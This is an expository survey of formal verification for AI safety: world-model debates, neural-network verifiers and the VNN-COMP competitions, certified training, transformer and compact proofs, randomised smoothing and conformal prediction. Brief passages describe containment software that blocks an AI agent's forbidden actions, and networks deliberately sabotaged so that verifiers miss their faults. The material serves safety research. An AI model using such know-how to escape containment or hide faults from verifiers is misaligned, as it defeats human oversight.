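Suppose a warehouse robot needs 1.5 seconds and 2 metres to stop. In the world model, people can walk in any direction at up to 2 metres per second, and the specification requires that the robot never be moving when it touches someone. A person can cover at most 3 metres while the robot brakes, so a robot that always starts braking while everyone is still more than 5 metres away meets the specification. This can be verified without predicting where anyone will walk. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest treating human behaviour this way, as a set of possibilities that the verifier must cover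 in full.

They also grade each part by how much safety it would provide if it worked, regardless of how feasible it is.

| Part | Lower levels | Middle levels | Upper levels |
|---|---|---|---|
| World model (0–5) | 0: none, with assumptions left implicit in the training data; 1: a trained black-box simulator | 2: a learned generator of causal models, tested against models that people have made; 3: causal models that human experts have fully audited | 4: models with a proof that they soundly simplify the laws of physics; 5: none, because the specification must hold in every possible world |
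| Safety specification (0–7) | 0: none; 1: human judges; 2: ordinary language that a black-box AI interprets | 3: hand-written formulas for limited properties; 4: formulas in which neural networks represent some concepts; 5: AI-written parts that people have audited | 6: hand-written formulas for comprehensive properties; 7: everything people might want, in all contexts |
| Verifier (0–10) | 0: no quantitative guarantee; 1–3: increasingly systematic tests | 4–5: automated searches for failures; 6–7: searches that would cover every input if they ran forever | 8: a search with a known limit on what it has missed so far; 9: a sound bound on the probability of failure; 10: the same, with a proof short enough for people to read |

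Strong guarantees need a verifier at level 8 or above. A high level in one part doesn't make up for a low level in another, because a level 10 proof about a level 1 simulator is only a proof about the simulator. Engineers already write good world models by hand when they know or control the environment, as they do for aircraft controllers. For systems that interact with human users, the economy or ecosystems, Dalrymple and colleagues expect AI will have to generate the model, perhaps as a program that people can read and audit.

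They also give a simple formula for how errors in the world model weaken the guarantee. If the model is wrong with probability at most q at each step, a system that is provably safe in the model for n steps is safe in reality with probability at least (1 − q)ⁿ. With q = 0.0001 and one step per second, this lower bound is 99% after 100 seconds but only 37% after 10,000 seconds (under three hours). The actual probability may be much higher, because many errors do no harm, but the proof does not establish that.

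One suggestion is to deploy a system for a limited time, then shut it down or switch it to a safe mode unless the verifier approves it again. This helps if the model's predictions become less accurate further into the future. But if the model has the same chance of being wrong at every step, the risk accumulates just as quickly with renewals as without them.

### The dispute over world models

In the best-known critique, *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, Andrew Dickson (2024) points out that existing proofs are about software and not about what happens in the physical world. Engineers used a formal tool to check the software that landed the Perseverance rover on Mars in 2021, but they proved nothing about the landing itself. In one analysis that Dickson cites, software accounts for about 20% of the risk of failure in Mars missions, so perfect software would leave the other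 80%.

Biology is the hardest case. Dalrymple and colleagues propose a system that would approve a DNA sequence for manufacture only after verifying that the risk of harmful use is below a set bound. Dickson replies that predicting precisely how a new virus affects people would require simulating a human body for years. In 2022, a leading simulation covered 20 minutes in the life of one unusually simple cell, and a body has about 36 trillion cells. The simulation would also need data on the body's starting state, and mapping just a millionth of a human brain produced 1.4 petabytes. Zac Hatfield-Dodds, who maintains a widely used software-testing library, says in the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* that screening DNA in this way would take "a thousand years of progress in microbiology".

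The framework paper contains both a narrow proposal and a broad one. A reader's comment on Dickson's post objects that the proposal was narrower than Dickson suggests, and quotes the paper's example of DNA synthesisers that provably cannot make *certain* pathogens. This narrow proposal is realistic, because a machine can compare a sequence with a list without any model of the human body, but it would not stop a new pathogen that is missing from the list. The broad proposal would stop one, but Dickson is right that nobody has the model it needs.

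*In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*, the main reply to the critics, written by a co-author of the framework, argues that a world model has to be accurate but not exact. "The temperature stays below 50 degrees" can be true and useful even if nobody can predict the temperature. The proof needs an over-approximation of the real world, like SLAM's simplified copy of a driver. Such a model doesn't need complete data about the starting state either, because bounds may be enough. This is a good answer to Dickson's claim that strong guarantees require precise simulation, and it means that the warehouse robot, for example, needs no model of the human brain.

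But over-approximation can make a system too cautious to be useful. If the robot must allow for someone in the warehouse sprinting at 10 metres per second, it has to start braking while that person is still 17 metres away, and in a busy building it would hardly move. The problem is worse for a chatbot. Worden (2026) argues in *AI and World Models* that large neural networks are intrinsically unreliable and have to be enclosed in a provably safe guardrail. To prove that a chatbot's guardrail lets through no harmful message, someone would need a model of how people react to what they read. A model that allows every possible reaction would be sound, but no message could be proved safe in it.

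The dispute is therefore about whether anyone can build models that are broad enough to be true and narrow enough to be useful. A critic commenting on *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* calls the claim that this is feasible "risible", and complains that advocates point to closed, well-understood domains when they discuss feasibility and to general AI when they discuss importance. The complaint seems fair, since the reply's examples of current or near-term uses are aviation, railways and autonomous vehicles. The reply also describes a table-tennis robot whose simulator represents the soft rubber of the bat with three extra springs. This was good enough for the robot to beat most human players, but the reply acknowledges that nobody has certified a bound on the simulator's error.

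In a comment responding to Dickson's post, Steve Omohundro, another co-author of the framework, argues that physicists already have a complete theory of everyday phenomena, and that engineers should design systems that can be verified instead of trying to verify whatever exists. Having a complete theory helps less than it seems to because, as another commenter notes, the approximations engineers use to get from fundamental physics to ordinary materials are specific to each application and often depend on measurements. Specification would remain a problem even if the physics were easy. A third commenter asks how anyone could specify that a program will never trigger an unknown bug in some database server elsewhere on the internet.

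Omohundro's advice about design is more convincing, since the designer of a computer chip or a warehouse can limit what a model of it has to cover. *Containment Verification* (2026) applies the same idea to AI agents. It proves that the software around an AI blocks forbidden actions whatever the AI outputs, so it needs no model of the AI. The guarantee holds only if every external effect passes through that software, and it does not cover deception or manipulation, which depend on what the AI's words mean to a reader.

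The two sides also disagree about how strong a guarantee has to be. Dickson accuses advocates of promising failure rates of zero, and would find their claims much more reasonable if they offered only rough estimates. The reply calls this a false choice, because a proof can also establish that the chance of overheating is at most 1%. Tegmark, in the talk *Provably Safe AI*, also asks for "quantitative safety bounds at least", as regulators do for drugs. The advocates are right about this, but the 1% bound is relative to the world model, so the real risk could be larger if the model is wrong.

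Hatfield-Dodds argues that the framework only moves the problem to showing that the world model matches reality. Dalrymple and colleagues answer that every approach to safety relies on assumptions about the world, and that a world model at least makes them explicit, so regulators and the public can challenge them. That is a good reason to write the assumptions down, but they may still be false.

They also suggest, less convincingly, that if AI systems can plan well enough to be dangerous, sufficiently accurate world models must be possible. But a planner needs to find only one course of action that works, whereas a safety proof has to cover everything that could go wrong.

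Some recent papers argue that verification is limited in principle. *Incompleteness of AI Safety Verification via Kolmogorov Complexity* (2026) shows that no fixed verifier can certify every safe case once the cases become complex enough, where a case's complexity is roughly the length of the shortest program that can produce it. This limits completeness, but a verifier can still be sound if it rejects whatever it cannot prove safe, though it will then block some safe actions. The paper suggests checking individual cases, which is close to how the framework verifies an AI's outputs one at a time. Young reports in *On the Computational, Informational, and Physical Foundations for AI Safety* that even simplified versions of a system checking the meaning of its own outputs are NP-complete, which means that no known method is fast in every case. Solvers often handle such problems in practice,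 so this result does not rule out useful guarantees either.

Dickson accepted that AI would make proofs easier but doubted that it would make modelling the world easier. The Salt project's 320,000 lines of Lean support his view of proofs. On modelling, research from 2026 offers promising methods but no sound model of an open environment. *World-Time Compute with Verified Code World Models* (2026) has AI write the world model as a readable program so that people can check whether it is coherent, though a coherent program can still describe the world incorrectly. *World Models in Pieces* (2026) certifies only those parts of an agent's internal model that its behaviour reliably supports, which at least shows where the model should not be trusted.

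*Foundation World Models for Agents that Learn, Verify, and Adapt Reliably* (2026) argues that agents should learn models whose error can be measured, and cites early results that suggest this is possible. The measured error could supply the q in the formula above. However, *Towards Safe World Models* (Yu, 2026), a survey of 163 works, concludes that accurate predictions alone do not make a world model safe to rely on, because mistakes in observation, memory or evaluation can still lead to unsafe decisions and persist through later updates. A low average error is therefore not enough for the proof, which needs a bound that also holds in rare situations, including new ones that the AI's own actions create. Nobody yet knows how to obtain such a bound outside environments that people have designed or can closely control.

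## Proving a property of a neural network

Once engineers have written a property and its assumptions, they can try to prove that a trained network satisfies it. A network with fixed weights is a long formula made of additions, multiplications and a simple non-linear function. The most common such function is relu(z), which equals z when z is positive and 0 otherwise. There are far too many possible inputs to test one at a time, so a verifier calculates with whole sets of them.

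### A worked example

A network with two inputs is enough to show the method. Let x₁ and x₂ each lie between −1 and 1, and let

h₁ = relu(x₁ + x₂), h₂ = relu(x₁ − x₂), y = h₁ + h₂.

Suppose the specification requires that y never exceed 2.5. A classifier's robustness can be specified in the same form, where y is the score of a wrong class minus the score of the right one, and the limit is 0.

The verifier first encodes a violation as a set of constraints: the ranges of x₁ and x₂, the definitions of h₁, h₂ and y, and y > 2.5. Most of these are linear, which solvers handle efficiently, but relu needs an either-or constraint. If z is the sum inside relu and h is the result, then either z ≤ 0 and h = 0, or z ≥ 0 and h = z. The property holds if no values satisfy all the constraints.

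The way to rule out a violation with the least computation is to pass ranges through the network. Both x₁ + x₂ and x₁ − x₂ lie between −2 and 2, so h₁ and h₂ lie between 0 and 2, and y is at most 4. This *interval bound* is sound, but it is too loose to prove that y ≤ 2.5, because it ignores the fact that h₁ and h₂ depend on the same inputs. The neuron h₁ reaches 2 only at x₁ = x₂ = 1, and h₂ reaches 2 only at x₁ = 1, x₂ = −1, so they cannot both reach 2 at once.

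A *linear relaxation* keeps that record by bounding each neuron with a formula instead of a number. Between z = −2 and z = 2, the graph of relu is flat up to 0 and then rises to 2. The straight line joining its two ends never falls below it, so relu(z) ≤ (z + 2)/2. Adding the bounds for the two neurons gives

y ≤ (x₁ + x₂ + 2)/2 + (x₁ − x₂ + 2)/2 = x₁ + 2 ≤ 3.

The bound is tighter because x₂ cancels. In general, if z ranges from a negative number l to a positive number u, the line is u(z − l)/(u − l). For lower bounds, any line αz with slope α between 0 and 1 stays on or below relu. Here the best slope is 0, which gives y ≥ 0. In a large network the best slope differs from neuron to neuron, and verifiers search for good slopes much as training searches for good weights. Researchers call this layer-by-layer calculation *bound propagation*.

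A bound of 3 still does not settle whether y can exceed 2.5. The relaxation is loose because relu bends at z = 0, so *branch and bound* splits the problem there. On each side of the bend, relu is exactly linear. The verifier splits first on the sign of x₁ + x₂, and then splits further only where it has to:

- If x₁ + x₂ ≤ 0, then h₁ = 0 and y = h₂, which is at most 2. No further split is necessary.
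- If x₁ + x₂ ≥ 0 and x₁ − x₂ ≥ 0, then y = (x₁ + x₂) + (x₁ − x₂) = 2x₁, which is at most 2.
- If x₁ + x₂ ≥ 0 and x₁ − x₂ ≤ 0, then h₂ = 0 and y = x₁ + x₂, which is at most 2.

These three cases cover every input, so y never exceeds 2 and the property holds. The smallest upper bound on y is 2, because y = 2 at x₁ = 1, x₂ = 0. If the specification had required y ≤ 1.5, that input would have been a counterexample. Verifiers usually search for a counterexample before attempting a proof, by repeatedly changing an input in a direction that increases y.

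### Why the cost can grow exponentially

Two neurons have four combinations of signs, and the proof needed three cases. Each added neuron can double the work, because n neurons have up to 2ⁿ combinations, or about 2 × 10⁹⁰ for 300 neurons.

Good bounds remove the need to check most of these cases. In the example, once x₁ + x₂ was negative, a single bound covered both signs of x₁ − x₂. Many neurons never need a split. If x₁ lies between 0.5 and 1 and x₂ between −0.4 and 0.4, then x₁ + x₂ and x₁ − x₂ are always positive, and the network is y = 2x₁. The time a proof takes therefore depends more on how many neurons could have either sign in the region than on the size of the network. Larger regions usually leave more neurons that could have either sign, which is one reason proofs of robustness tend to cover only very small changes to an image.

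Some verifiers split the input ranges instead. Cutting the range of x₁ at 0 lowers the linear bound on y from 3 to about 2.67, and cutting the upper half again at 0.5 lowers it to 2.4, which proves the property. This works well for networks with few inputs, but with a thousand inputs, halving every range just once would produce 2¹⁰⁰⁰ pieces.

Choosing the splits cleverly is unlikely to remove the problem entirely. Guy Katz and colleagues proved in 2017 that deciding whether a relu network can violate a property is NP-complete. Their proof represents a logic puzzle as a network, with inputs of 0 and 1 standing for false and true. The neuron relu(1 − a − b − c) equals 1 if a, b and c are all false, and 0 if at least one is true, so it detects a violation of the rule "a or b or c". The network has one such neuron for each rule, and others that force the inputs to be 0 or 1, so it can output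 zero violations exactly when all the rules can hold together. A verifier that was fast on every network would therefore solve every such puzzle quickly, which nobody knows how to do.

### From Reluplex to the 2026 competition

The same 2017 paper introduced Reluplex, the first widely known verifier for networks of practical interest. Reluplex extends the simplex algorithm, a standard method for solving linear constraints. It temporarily allows values that violate the relation between z and relu(z), repairs them as it runs, and splits the problem into cases only when the repairs keep failing.

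Katz and colleagues tested their verification method on ACAS Xu, a system that advises unmanned aircraft how to avoid collisions. The system uses 45 networks, each with 300 neurons, five inputs that describe the two aircraft, and five outputs that score the possible advisories. One of the ten properties they checked says that if another aircraft is straight ahead and approaching, the network must not advise "clear of conflict". They checked four of the properties on every network and the other six on one network each, for a total of 186 cases. In the original experiments, running times ranged from seconds to days, and some runs never finished.

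These cases are now a routine test in VNN-COMP, an annual competition for network verifiers that began in 2020. In 2026 the time limit was 116 seconds per case. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) reports that three tools settled all 186 cases, often in about two seconds. They proved 139 and found counterexamples to the other 47.

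Eleven teams entered 13 tools in the 2026 competition. The regular track had 24 benchmarks with 3,373 cases, and an extended track had six more benchmarks with 245 cases. Each case consists of a network, a property and a time limit, and the organisers run every tool on rented machines of equal cost. A correct proof or counterexample earns 10 points, a wrong answer loses 150, and an answer of "unknown" or a timeout earns nothing. The organisers then rescale the points so that the best tool on each benchmark gets 100.

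The winner, α,β-CROWN, combines linear bounds with branch and bound on a graphics processor. It settled 3,164 of the regular cases, or 94%. Its results on six of the benchmarks show that size is a poor guide to difficulty:

| Benchmark | Parameters per network | Cases | Proved | Refuted | Unsettled |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| safeNLP (sentence filters) | 4,000 | 1,080 | 418 | 662 | 0 |
| ACAS Xu | 13,000 | 186 | 139 | 47 | 0 |
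| Vision transformers | 68,000–76,000 | 200 | 123 | 0 | 77 |
| Traffic signs | 0.9–1.8 million | 45 | 0 | 36 | 9 |
| CIFAR-100 (small photographs) | 2.5–3.8 million | 200 | 127 | 33 | 40 |
| VGG-16 (large photographs) | 138 million | 18 | 18 | 0 | 0 |

VGG-16 is about 1,800 times as large as the vision transformers, yet α,β-CROWN proved every property of it. Some of those properties allow only one pixel to change, which keeps the ranges inside the network narrow. No tool proved any property of the traffic-sign networks, whose weights and neuron outputs are mostly restricted to +1 and −1.

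Two researchers at Stony Brook University, one of them also an organiser of the competition, had the AI coding tool Claude Code write the runner-up, a verifier called Vibecheck, over two months. Vibecheck settled 3,108 regular cases, and the organisers recorded no wrong answers from it. This is strong evidence that AI can now build a competitive verifier, though a clean record on these benchmarks does not prove that Vibecheck is sound.

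*The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025) reports only seven ranked tools, on 16 regular and nine extended benchmarks. The winner and the most successful combination of methods stayed the same. The specification language, VNN-LIB, changed more. A VNN-LIB file describes what a counterexample would look like. Version 1.0 had no precisely defined syntax, so each team wrote its own program to read it, and the programs accepted slightly different files. It also couldn't express a property that involves two runs of one network, such as "two applicants who differ only in age get the same decision".

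Version 2.0, released in 2026, has a formal grammar and allows such comparisons. One new benchmark uses it to check ACAS Xu networks for *monotonicity*, which requires comparing the outputs for a smaller and a larger input. Four tools found counterexamples in all 50 cases.

### Wrong answers and rounding errors

The organisers of VNN-COMP usually do not know the right answer in advance. When tools disagree, the one that reports a violation must supply a counterexample, because anyone can check it by running the network on it. A reported proof therefore counts as correct unless some tool finds a valid counterexample. One entrant, SobolBox, samples a network's outputs and searches for the extremes. If the extremes it finds obey the property, it reports a proof, although its developer describes these results as unsound. SobolBox earned points for 204 of these reported proofs in 2026.

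The organisers recorded 1,135 wrong answers in the regular track that year. This total includes invalid and missing counterexamples as well as false proofs, so it does not measure how often a tool claimed to have proved a false property. Of the wrong answers, 955 came from Agate, a new tool in which a last-minute bug corrupted the counterexamples. NeuralSAT, which came fourth overall, had 94. It gave 963 right answers and 86 wrong ones on the sentence filters, which left it with −3,270 points and a score of zero on that benchmark.

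Even α,β-CROWN gave one wrong answer, on a benchmark whose designers had hidden counterexamples that ordinary searches tend to miss. It settled 59 of the 60 cases correctly, but the penalty for its wrong answer put it behind Vibecheck, which settled 53 and made no mistakes. The penalty is appropriate because a false proof is worse for anyone who relies on it than an answer of "unknown".

Some disagreements come from *floating-point* arithmetic, in which a computer stores each number with a limited number of digits and rounds the rest. In 2025, Kaulen and colleagues found counterexamples that violated a property on one machine but not on another. A referee can allow for rounding by accepting outputs that miss a violation by a tiny amount, but this changes the property being checked. In the worked example, y ≤ 2 is true, but a referee who counts any y above 1.999999 as a violation would accept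 x₁ = 1, x₂ = 0 as a counterexample and penalise a tool that had correctly proved the property. Kaulen and colleagues scored the 2025 results both ways and found 62 wrong answers with no tolerance and 495 with a tolerance of one millionth, 437 of them from SobolBox.

The organisers adopted a compromise for 2026. The input of a counterexample must satisfy the specification exactly, and a fixed version of standard software computes the output. If that output violates the property exactly, the counterexample refutes any reported proof. If the output falls short of a violation by no more than 0.0001, the tool that found the counterexample gets full points, but so do the tools that reported a proof. This makes the scoring reproducible, but it cannot determine which tool is right in the closest cases, because the reference software also rounds its numbers.

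Verifiers generally prove statements about a network in exact arithmetic. Such a proof does not by itself cover the network people run, which rounds at every step and can give different results depending on the order of the steps. In ordinary double precision, 2⁵³ + 1 − 2⁵³ gives 0, but 2⁵³ − 2⁵³ + 1 gives 1. In *No Soundness in the Real World*, Szász, Bánhelyi and Jelasity (2025) used such differences to build networks that work normally on some computers and misclassify nearly everything on others. Every verifier they tested missed the fault in at least some of the networks. These networks were deliberately sabotaged, and an honestly trained network is unlikely to change so drastically.

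A verifier can close this gap by following the same order of operations and rounding as the deployed network. That requires detailed knowledge of the deployment, and on parallel hardware the order can vary from run to run. Another approach is to verify the program code that runs the network. *Floating-Point Neural Network Verification at the Software Level* (2025) provides 912 C programs with known verdicts for testing code verifiers on neural networks. The programs range from single functions to whole networks.

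Bugs in the verifier itself need a different remedy, called a certificate. A certificate can list the cases and, for each one, the multipliers that produce a contradiction, so that checking it takes only simple arithmetic. In the second case of the worked example, y = 2x₁, so a violation needs 2x₁ > 2.5. Multiplying the constraint x₁ ≤ 1 by 2 gives 2x₁ ≤ 2, which contradicts this. Desmartin, Isac and colleagues built a checker for proofs from the verifier Marabou. The organisers of VNN-COMP hope eventually to require certificates from every tool, which would end the practice of counting a proof as correct because nobody has refuted it. A certificate of this kind still proves the property only for exact arithmetic, so it does not solve the rounding problem.

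### Training networks that are easier to verify

Developers can also make proofs easier by changing the network. Ordinary training reduces the error on each example, while *certified training* computes bounds for a region around each example, often with intervals, and reduces the worst error those bounds allow. The trained network then tends to have tight bounds.

Training that rewards tight bounds can reduce accuracy, as the worked example shows. Suppose the correct function is relu(x₁ + x₂) + relu(x₁ − x₂). Intervals give a maximum of 4, twice the true value. For the simpler function relu(2x₁), intervals give exactly 2. The two functions agree wherever x₁ is at least as large as both x₂ and −x₂, but at x₁ = 0, x₂ = 1 the correct answer is 1 and the simpler function gives 0. The training favours functions like the simpler one because their bounds are tighter, even where they fit the data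 less well.

One of the 2026 benchmarks uses networks trained in this way. Ladner and colleagues list their ordinary accuracy and their *certified accuracy*, which is the share of test images that a network classifies correctly and on which a verifier proved it robust. On CIFAR-10, a standard set of small photographs in ten classes, ordinary networks exceed 90% accuracy. Certified training for changes of up to 2 brightness steps out of 255 per pixel gave 83.5% accuracy and 66.0% certified accuracy. For changes of up to 8 steps, which are still hard to see, the figures fell to 57.2% and 35.5%. On Tiny ImageNet, which has 200 classes, the best certified accuracy was 28.4% for a change of one step.

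Part of the shortfall comes from the verifier running out of time. On a wider version of the first CIFAR-10 network, accuracy rose to 85.4% but certified accuracy fell to 60.3%, because the verifier had not settled 14.3% of the cases after 1,000 seconds each. If all of those images were robust, the true figure would be 74.6%, compared with at most 72.6% for the narrower network under the same assumption. The wider network may therefore be more robust, but these results don't establish that. Across six such networks, the verifier ran out of time on 2,994 of 60,000 cases, which took about 35 days of machine time.

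When this takes too much computation, developers can use *randomised smoothing*, which runs the network on many noisy copies of the input and gives a guarantee that holds with a stated probability.

### What is possible for transformers

Language models are transformers, which process a list of tokens (or image patches). An operation called *attention* determines how much each token draws on the others. It multiplies quantities that all depend on the input and then applies exponentials, so a verifier must relax more complicated functions than relu. Slack in the bounds also accumulates from layer to layer.

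The vision transformers in VNN-COMP are small for this reason. They have two or three layers and classify about 60% of CIFAR-10 images correctly. Their designers also replaced one standard component with another that is easier to verify. The property is robustness to a change of one brightness step per pixel. The tool α,β-CROWN proved 123 of the 200 cases. Another tool, ACT, reported proofs of all 200. However, the designers had removed nearly every case for which they could find a counterexample, so the benchmark would probably not expose a false proof. ACT also gave ten wrong answers on other benchmarks. Its 200 reported proofs therefore need independent confirmation.

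Text is harder to verify than images because a token can't be changed slightly, the way a pixel can be made slightly brighter. Checking every input is infeasible, since a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens allows about 10⁴⁷ sequences of ten tokens. *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* (2026) points out that any sound verifier that treats the model as a black box may have to query all of them. A practical verifier therefore has to use the model's structure, and it needs a set of inputs that a short rule can describe.

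The sentence filters in the competition avoid this problem by leaving the language model out of the proof. A language model turns each sentence into a list of numbers, reduced to 30 for the benchmark, and a small network uses those numbers to decide whether, for example, the user is asking if the chatbot is human. The designers collect rewordings of a sentence, draw the smallest box around their numbers and check whether the small network gives the right answer everywhere in the box. The network failed this check for 662 of the 1,080 boxes. A proof for one of the other boxes covers the small network but not the language model that supplies the numbers, and a new rewording may fall outside the box.

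Researchers have also begun to prove properties of some internal parts of language models. In *The Misery of Mechanistic Interpretability*, Ladner and Althoff (2026) study GPT-2, a language model from 2019. *Mechanistic interpretability* tries to explain a network's calculations in terms people can understand. One of its tools is a *sparse autoencoder*, a second network that rewrites a layer's values as a short list of features with labels such as "workplace culture". An auditor who reads the labels needs to know that the rewritten values stay close to the originals. Ladner and Althoff proved limits on how far the two can differ within regions that represent replacing words with synonyms.

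The limits were reasonably tight in an early layer and much looser in later ones. Retraining one autoencoder with the verifier's bounds in mind reduced its limit by about 90%. Even then, only two or three of the 20 strongest features were guaranteed to survive synonym substitution. Some of the instability comes from GPT-2 itself, whose next-token prediction changed for 21% of one-word substitutions.

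Ladner and Althoff state that current verifiers do not yet scale to the full model. They had to construct the region separately at each layer instead of carrying it through from the input, so their results do not provide a guarantee about GPT-2's output. *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) begins to connect layers. It certifies attention in GPT-2's first layer, taking about a second per sample, and then extends the calculation to the second layer. The tests cover 480 queries from five samples.

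### Compact proofs

In *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability* (2024), Jason Gross and colleagues prove a lower bound on a model's accuracy over all inputs, rather than its robustness near one input. They use an explanation of how the model works to make the proof short.

The models are one-layer transformers that read a few numbers and output the largest. With four numbers, each from 0 to 63, there are about 17 million possible inputs. Running the model on all of them proves its exact accuracy, but each extra number multiplies the work by 64. Understanding how the model works allows a shorter proof. In these models, attention favours larger numbers, and the model copies the number that receives the most attention to the output. A proof can therefore check, for each possible maximum, that it receives enough attention to outweigh the worst possible effect of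 the other numbers. This takes far fewer steps because it covers large groups of inputs together.

This proof gives a weaker bound because it has to assume that the worst attention and the worst copying error occur together, just as the interval bound assumed that h₁ and h₂ reach 2 together. Gross and colleagues compared 102 proof strategies on 151 trained models and found that shorter proofs required more understanding of the model, while more faithful explanations gave tighter bounds. A compact proof therefore also tests an explanation, since an explanation that overlooks something important will yield a poor bound.

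Later work extended the method to other small problems. Wu, Jaburi and colleagues (2024) applied it to networks that had learned the multiplication tables of finite groups. Their proof took about 30% of the time needed to try every input, and guaranteed at least 95% accuracy for 45% of the networks. For the rest, the explanation of how the network worked was incomplete or the bound on its accuracy was too loose. Yip, Agrawal and colleagues (2024) studied networks that do addition that wraps around like the hours on a clock, and obtained useful bounds on the non-linear part of the network without trying every input.

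All these tasks have an exact right answer and few enough inputs that someone can check the proof by brute force. Gross and colleagues identify the main obstacle to going further as *noise*, the small parts of the weights that the explanation does not account for. These parts mostly cancel out in practice, but a proof has to allow for all of them pushing in the same harmful direction, and that allowance grows with more layers. The largest language models are thousands of times the size of GPT-2, and nobody has a nearly complete explanation of one. A compact proof about such a model would need that explanation, a way to bound what it leaves out, and a formal definition of a right answer, which most conversations do not have.

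## Guarantees that hold with a stated probability

Exact proofs become infeasible long before a network reaches the size of a modern language model. Engineers can still run a large model on many randomly chosen inputs, count the failures and calculate how high the true failure rate could plausibly be. They don't need access to the model's weights. The resulting guarantee covers the average failure rate over the distribution the inputs were drawn from, rather than every input, and it has a small chance of being wrong.

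### Failure rate and confidence

A test might show, with 95% confidence, that a system fails on at most 0.1% of inputs. The 95% describes the test's reliability: if the true failure rate were above 0.1%, the test would wrongly pass the system at most 5% of the time. *Bounding the Black Box* (2026) proposes such tests for regulating AI and points out that legal frameworks would have to allow explicitly for this chance of error.

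In the simplest case, n independent trials produce no failures. If the failure rate is p, this happens with probability (1 − p)ⁿ. The largest p for which that probability is still at least 5% is

p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n,

because the natural logarithm of 20 is about 3. So 3,000 trials without a failure support a bound of 0.1%, and a bound of one in a million takes about three million trials. Raising the confidence is cheap by comparison. At 99.9% the 3 becomes 6.9, so a chance of error 50 times smaller costs little more than twice as many trials.

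When some trials fail, statisticians usually use the Clopper–Pearson bound (1934). It is the failure rate at which there would be a 5% chance of seeing as few failures as were observed, or fewer. One failure in n trials gives a bound of about 4.7/n, and three failures give about 7.8/n. Simpler formulas can give much looser bounds. *Bounding the Black Box* uses Hoeffding's inequality, which gives a bound of 2.2% for 3,000 trials without a failure, while Clopper–Pearson gives 0.1%. The paper acknowledges that developers might have to retrain or abandon models that are in fact safe enough.

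All these bounds assume that the trials are independent and come from the distribution the system will face in use. Testers also have to decide in advance what counts as passing and how many times they will try. If a developer tests 20 versions that all fail slightly too often, about one of them will pass by luck.

### Randomised smoothing

Sampling can also establish robustness around a single input. Randomised smoothing turns any classifier f into a new classifier g. To classify an image x, g adds random noise to every pixel, runs f on many noisy copies and returns the most common class. The noise follows a bell curve with standard deviation σ. Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter (2019), in *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing*, proved that g's answer stays the same for every change to x smaller than

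R = σΦ⁻¹(p),

where p is a lower confidence bound on the probability that f gives a noisy copy the top class, and must exceed one half. Φ⁻¹(p) is the number of standard deviations from the mean below which a bell-curve variable falls with probability p. The size of a change here is the square root of the sum of the squared pixel changes, rather than the largest change to any one pixel.

Moving x moves the whole cloud of noisy copies by the same distance. The new cloud overlaps the old one, which limits how much f's answers can change. The worst possible f has a flat boundary across the attacker's path, with the right class on the near side and a wrong class on the far side. If p = 0.9, this boundary is 1.28σ from x, so the attacker has to move the cloud that far before half of it crosses. For σ = 0.5, R is therefore about 0.64. The proof assumes nothing else about f, so the method works for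 networks of any size.

The number of samples limits the radius. If f assigns all 1,000 noisy copies to the same class, the lower bound on p at 99.9% confidence is 0.001^(1/1000), or about 0.993. For σ = 0.5 this gives R ≈ 1.23, even if f would give the same answer everywhere. With 100,000 agreeing copies, R rises only to about 1.91. Adding noise increases the radius faster, but it also obscures the image.

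Cohen and colleagues tested this on 500 photographs from ImageNet, which has 1,000 classes. For each photograph, they used 100 noisy copies to guess the top class and another 100,000 to bound that class's probability with 99.9% confidence. This took 110 seconds per photograph. They trained f on noisy images and chose the best noise level for each radius.

| Radius | Correct, with a certificate for at least this radius | Correct, with or without a certificate |
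|---|---|---|
| 0.5 | 49% | 67% |
| 1.0 | 37% | 57% |
| 2.0 | 19% | 57% |
| 3.0 | 12% | 44% |

Within a radius of 0.5, an attacker can change a single pixel value by half its full range, or all of the roughly 150,000 values in such an image by only about a third of one brightness step each.

The certificate applies to g, so a company that certifies g and then deploys f to save computing time has no guarantee. The certificate shows that the answer is stable, but a stable answer may still be wrong. Rotating or cropping an image usually changes it by more than R, and Cohen and colleagues proved that the sampled probabilities alone cannot justify a larger radius. In use, g relies on a limited number of noisy copies and abstains when the vote is close, so an attacker can make it abstain by finding a change within the radius that brings the vote close to a tie. Each certificate also has up to a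 0.1% chance of being wrong, so a million of them could include about 1,000 errors.

Within those limits, the guarantee holds even if an attacker picks the worst possible change, because the defender draws the noise afterwards.

### Conformal prediction

A classifier that often has low confidence in any single answer can still be useful if it gives a set of possible answers. *Conformal prediction* makes the set large enough to contain the right answer with a chosen probability, say 90%.

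Suppose a hospital has 99 diagnosed cases that its model did not train on. For each case, it computes an error score, such as one minus the probability the model gave to the correct diagnosis. The 90th smallest score is 0.7. For a new patient, the set contains every diagnosis with a score of 0.7 or less, which means those the model considers at least 30% probable. The new patient's correct diagnosis also has a score, which is equally likely to have any rank from 1 to 100 among the 100 scores. The probability that it is one of the 90 smallest, and that the correct diagnosis is therefore in the set, is at least 90%. A poor model has the same guarantee as a good one but produces larger sets.

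The ranking argument needs the cases to be *exchangeable*, meaning that every order of the hundred cases is equally probable. Independent draws from one distribution satisfy this. The condition may fail for patients from a different hospital, or for next winter's patients if a new virus is spreading. Any threshold set on past data can miss its target error rate after such a shift. In *Provable Limits and Certified Deferral for Verbalized Uncertainty in Small Language Models* (2026), thresholds chosen on one set of questions to keep a model's error rate below 20% let it exceed that limit by up to about 30 percentage points on another set.

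The 90% is also an average over patients. If one group makes up nine-tenths of the patients, the sets could contain the right diagnosis for 95% of that group and only 45% of everyone else.

Researchers have adapted the method to language models. *COFT* (2026) uses it to choose each next token, allowing only tokens that are plausible both for the original prompt and for a version that changes a protected attribute, such as gender. *C-SafeGen* (2026) bounds the risk that a model produces text that a fixed guardrail model judges unsafe. Exchangeability is hard to justify for a public chatbot because users change what they ask as they learn what it can do.

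### FairSquare and probabilities without sampling

A property about probabilities can have an exact proof. *Fairness as a Program Property* (Albarghouthi, D'Antoni and Drews, 2016) treats fairness as a property of a decision-making program, to be verified relative to a *population model*, a distribution over applicants that has the same role as D.

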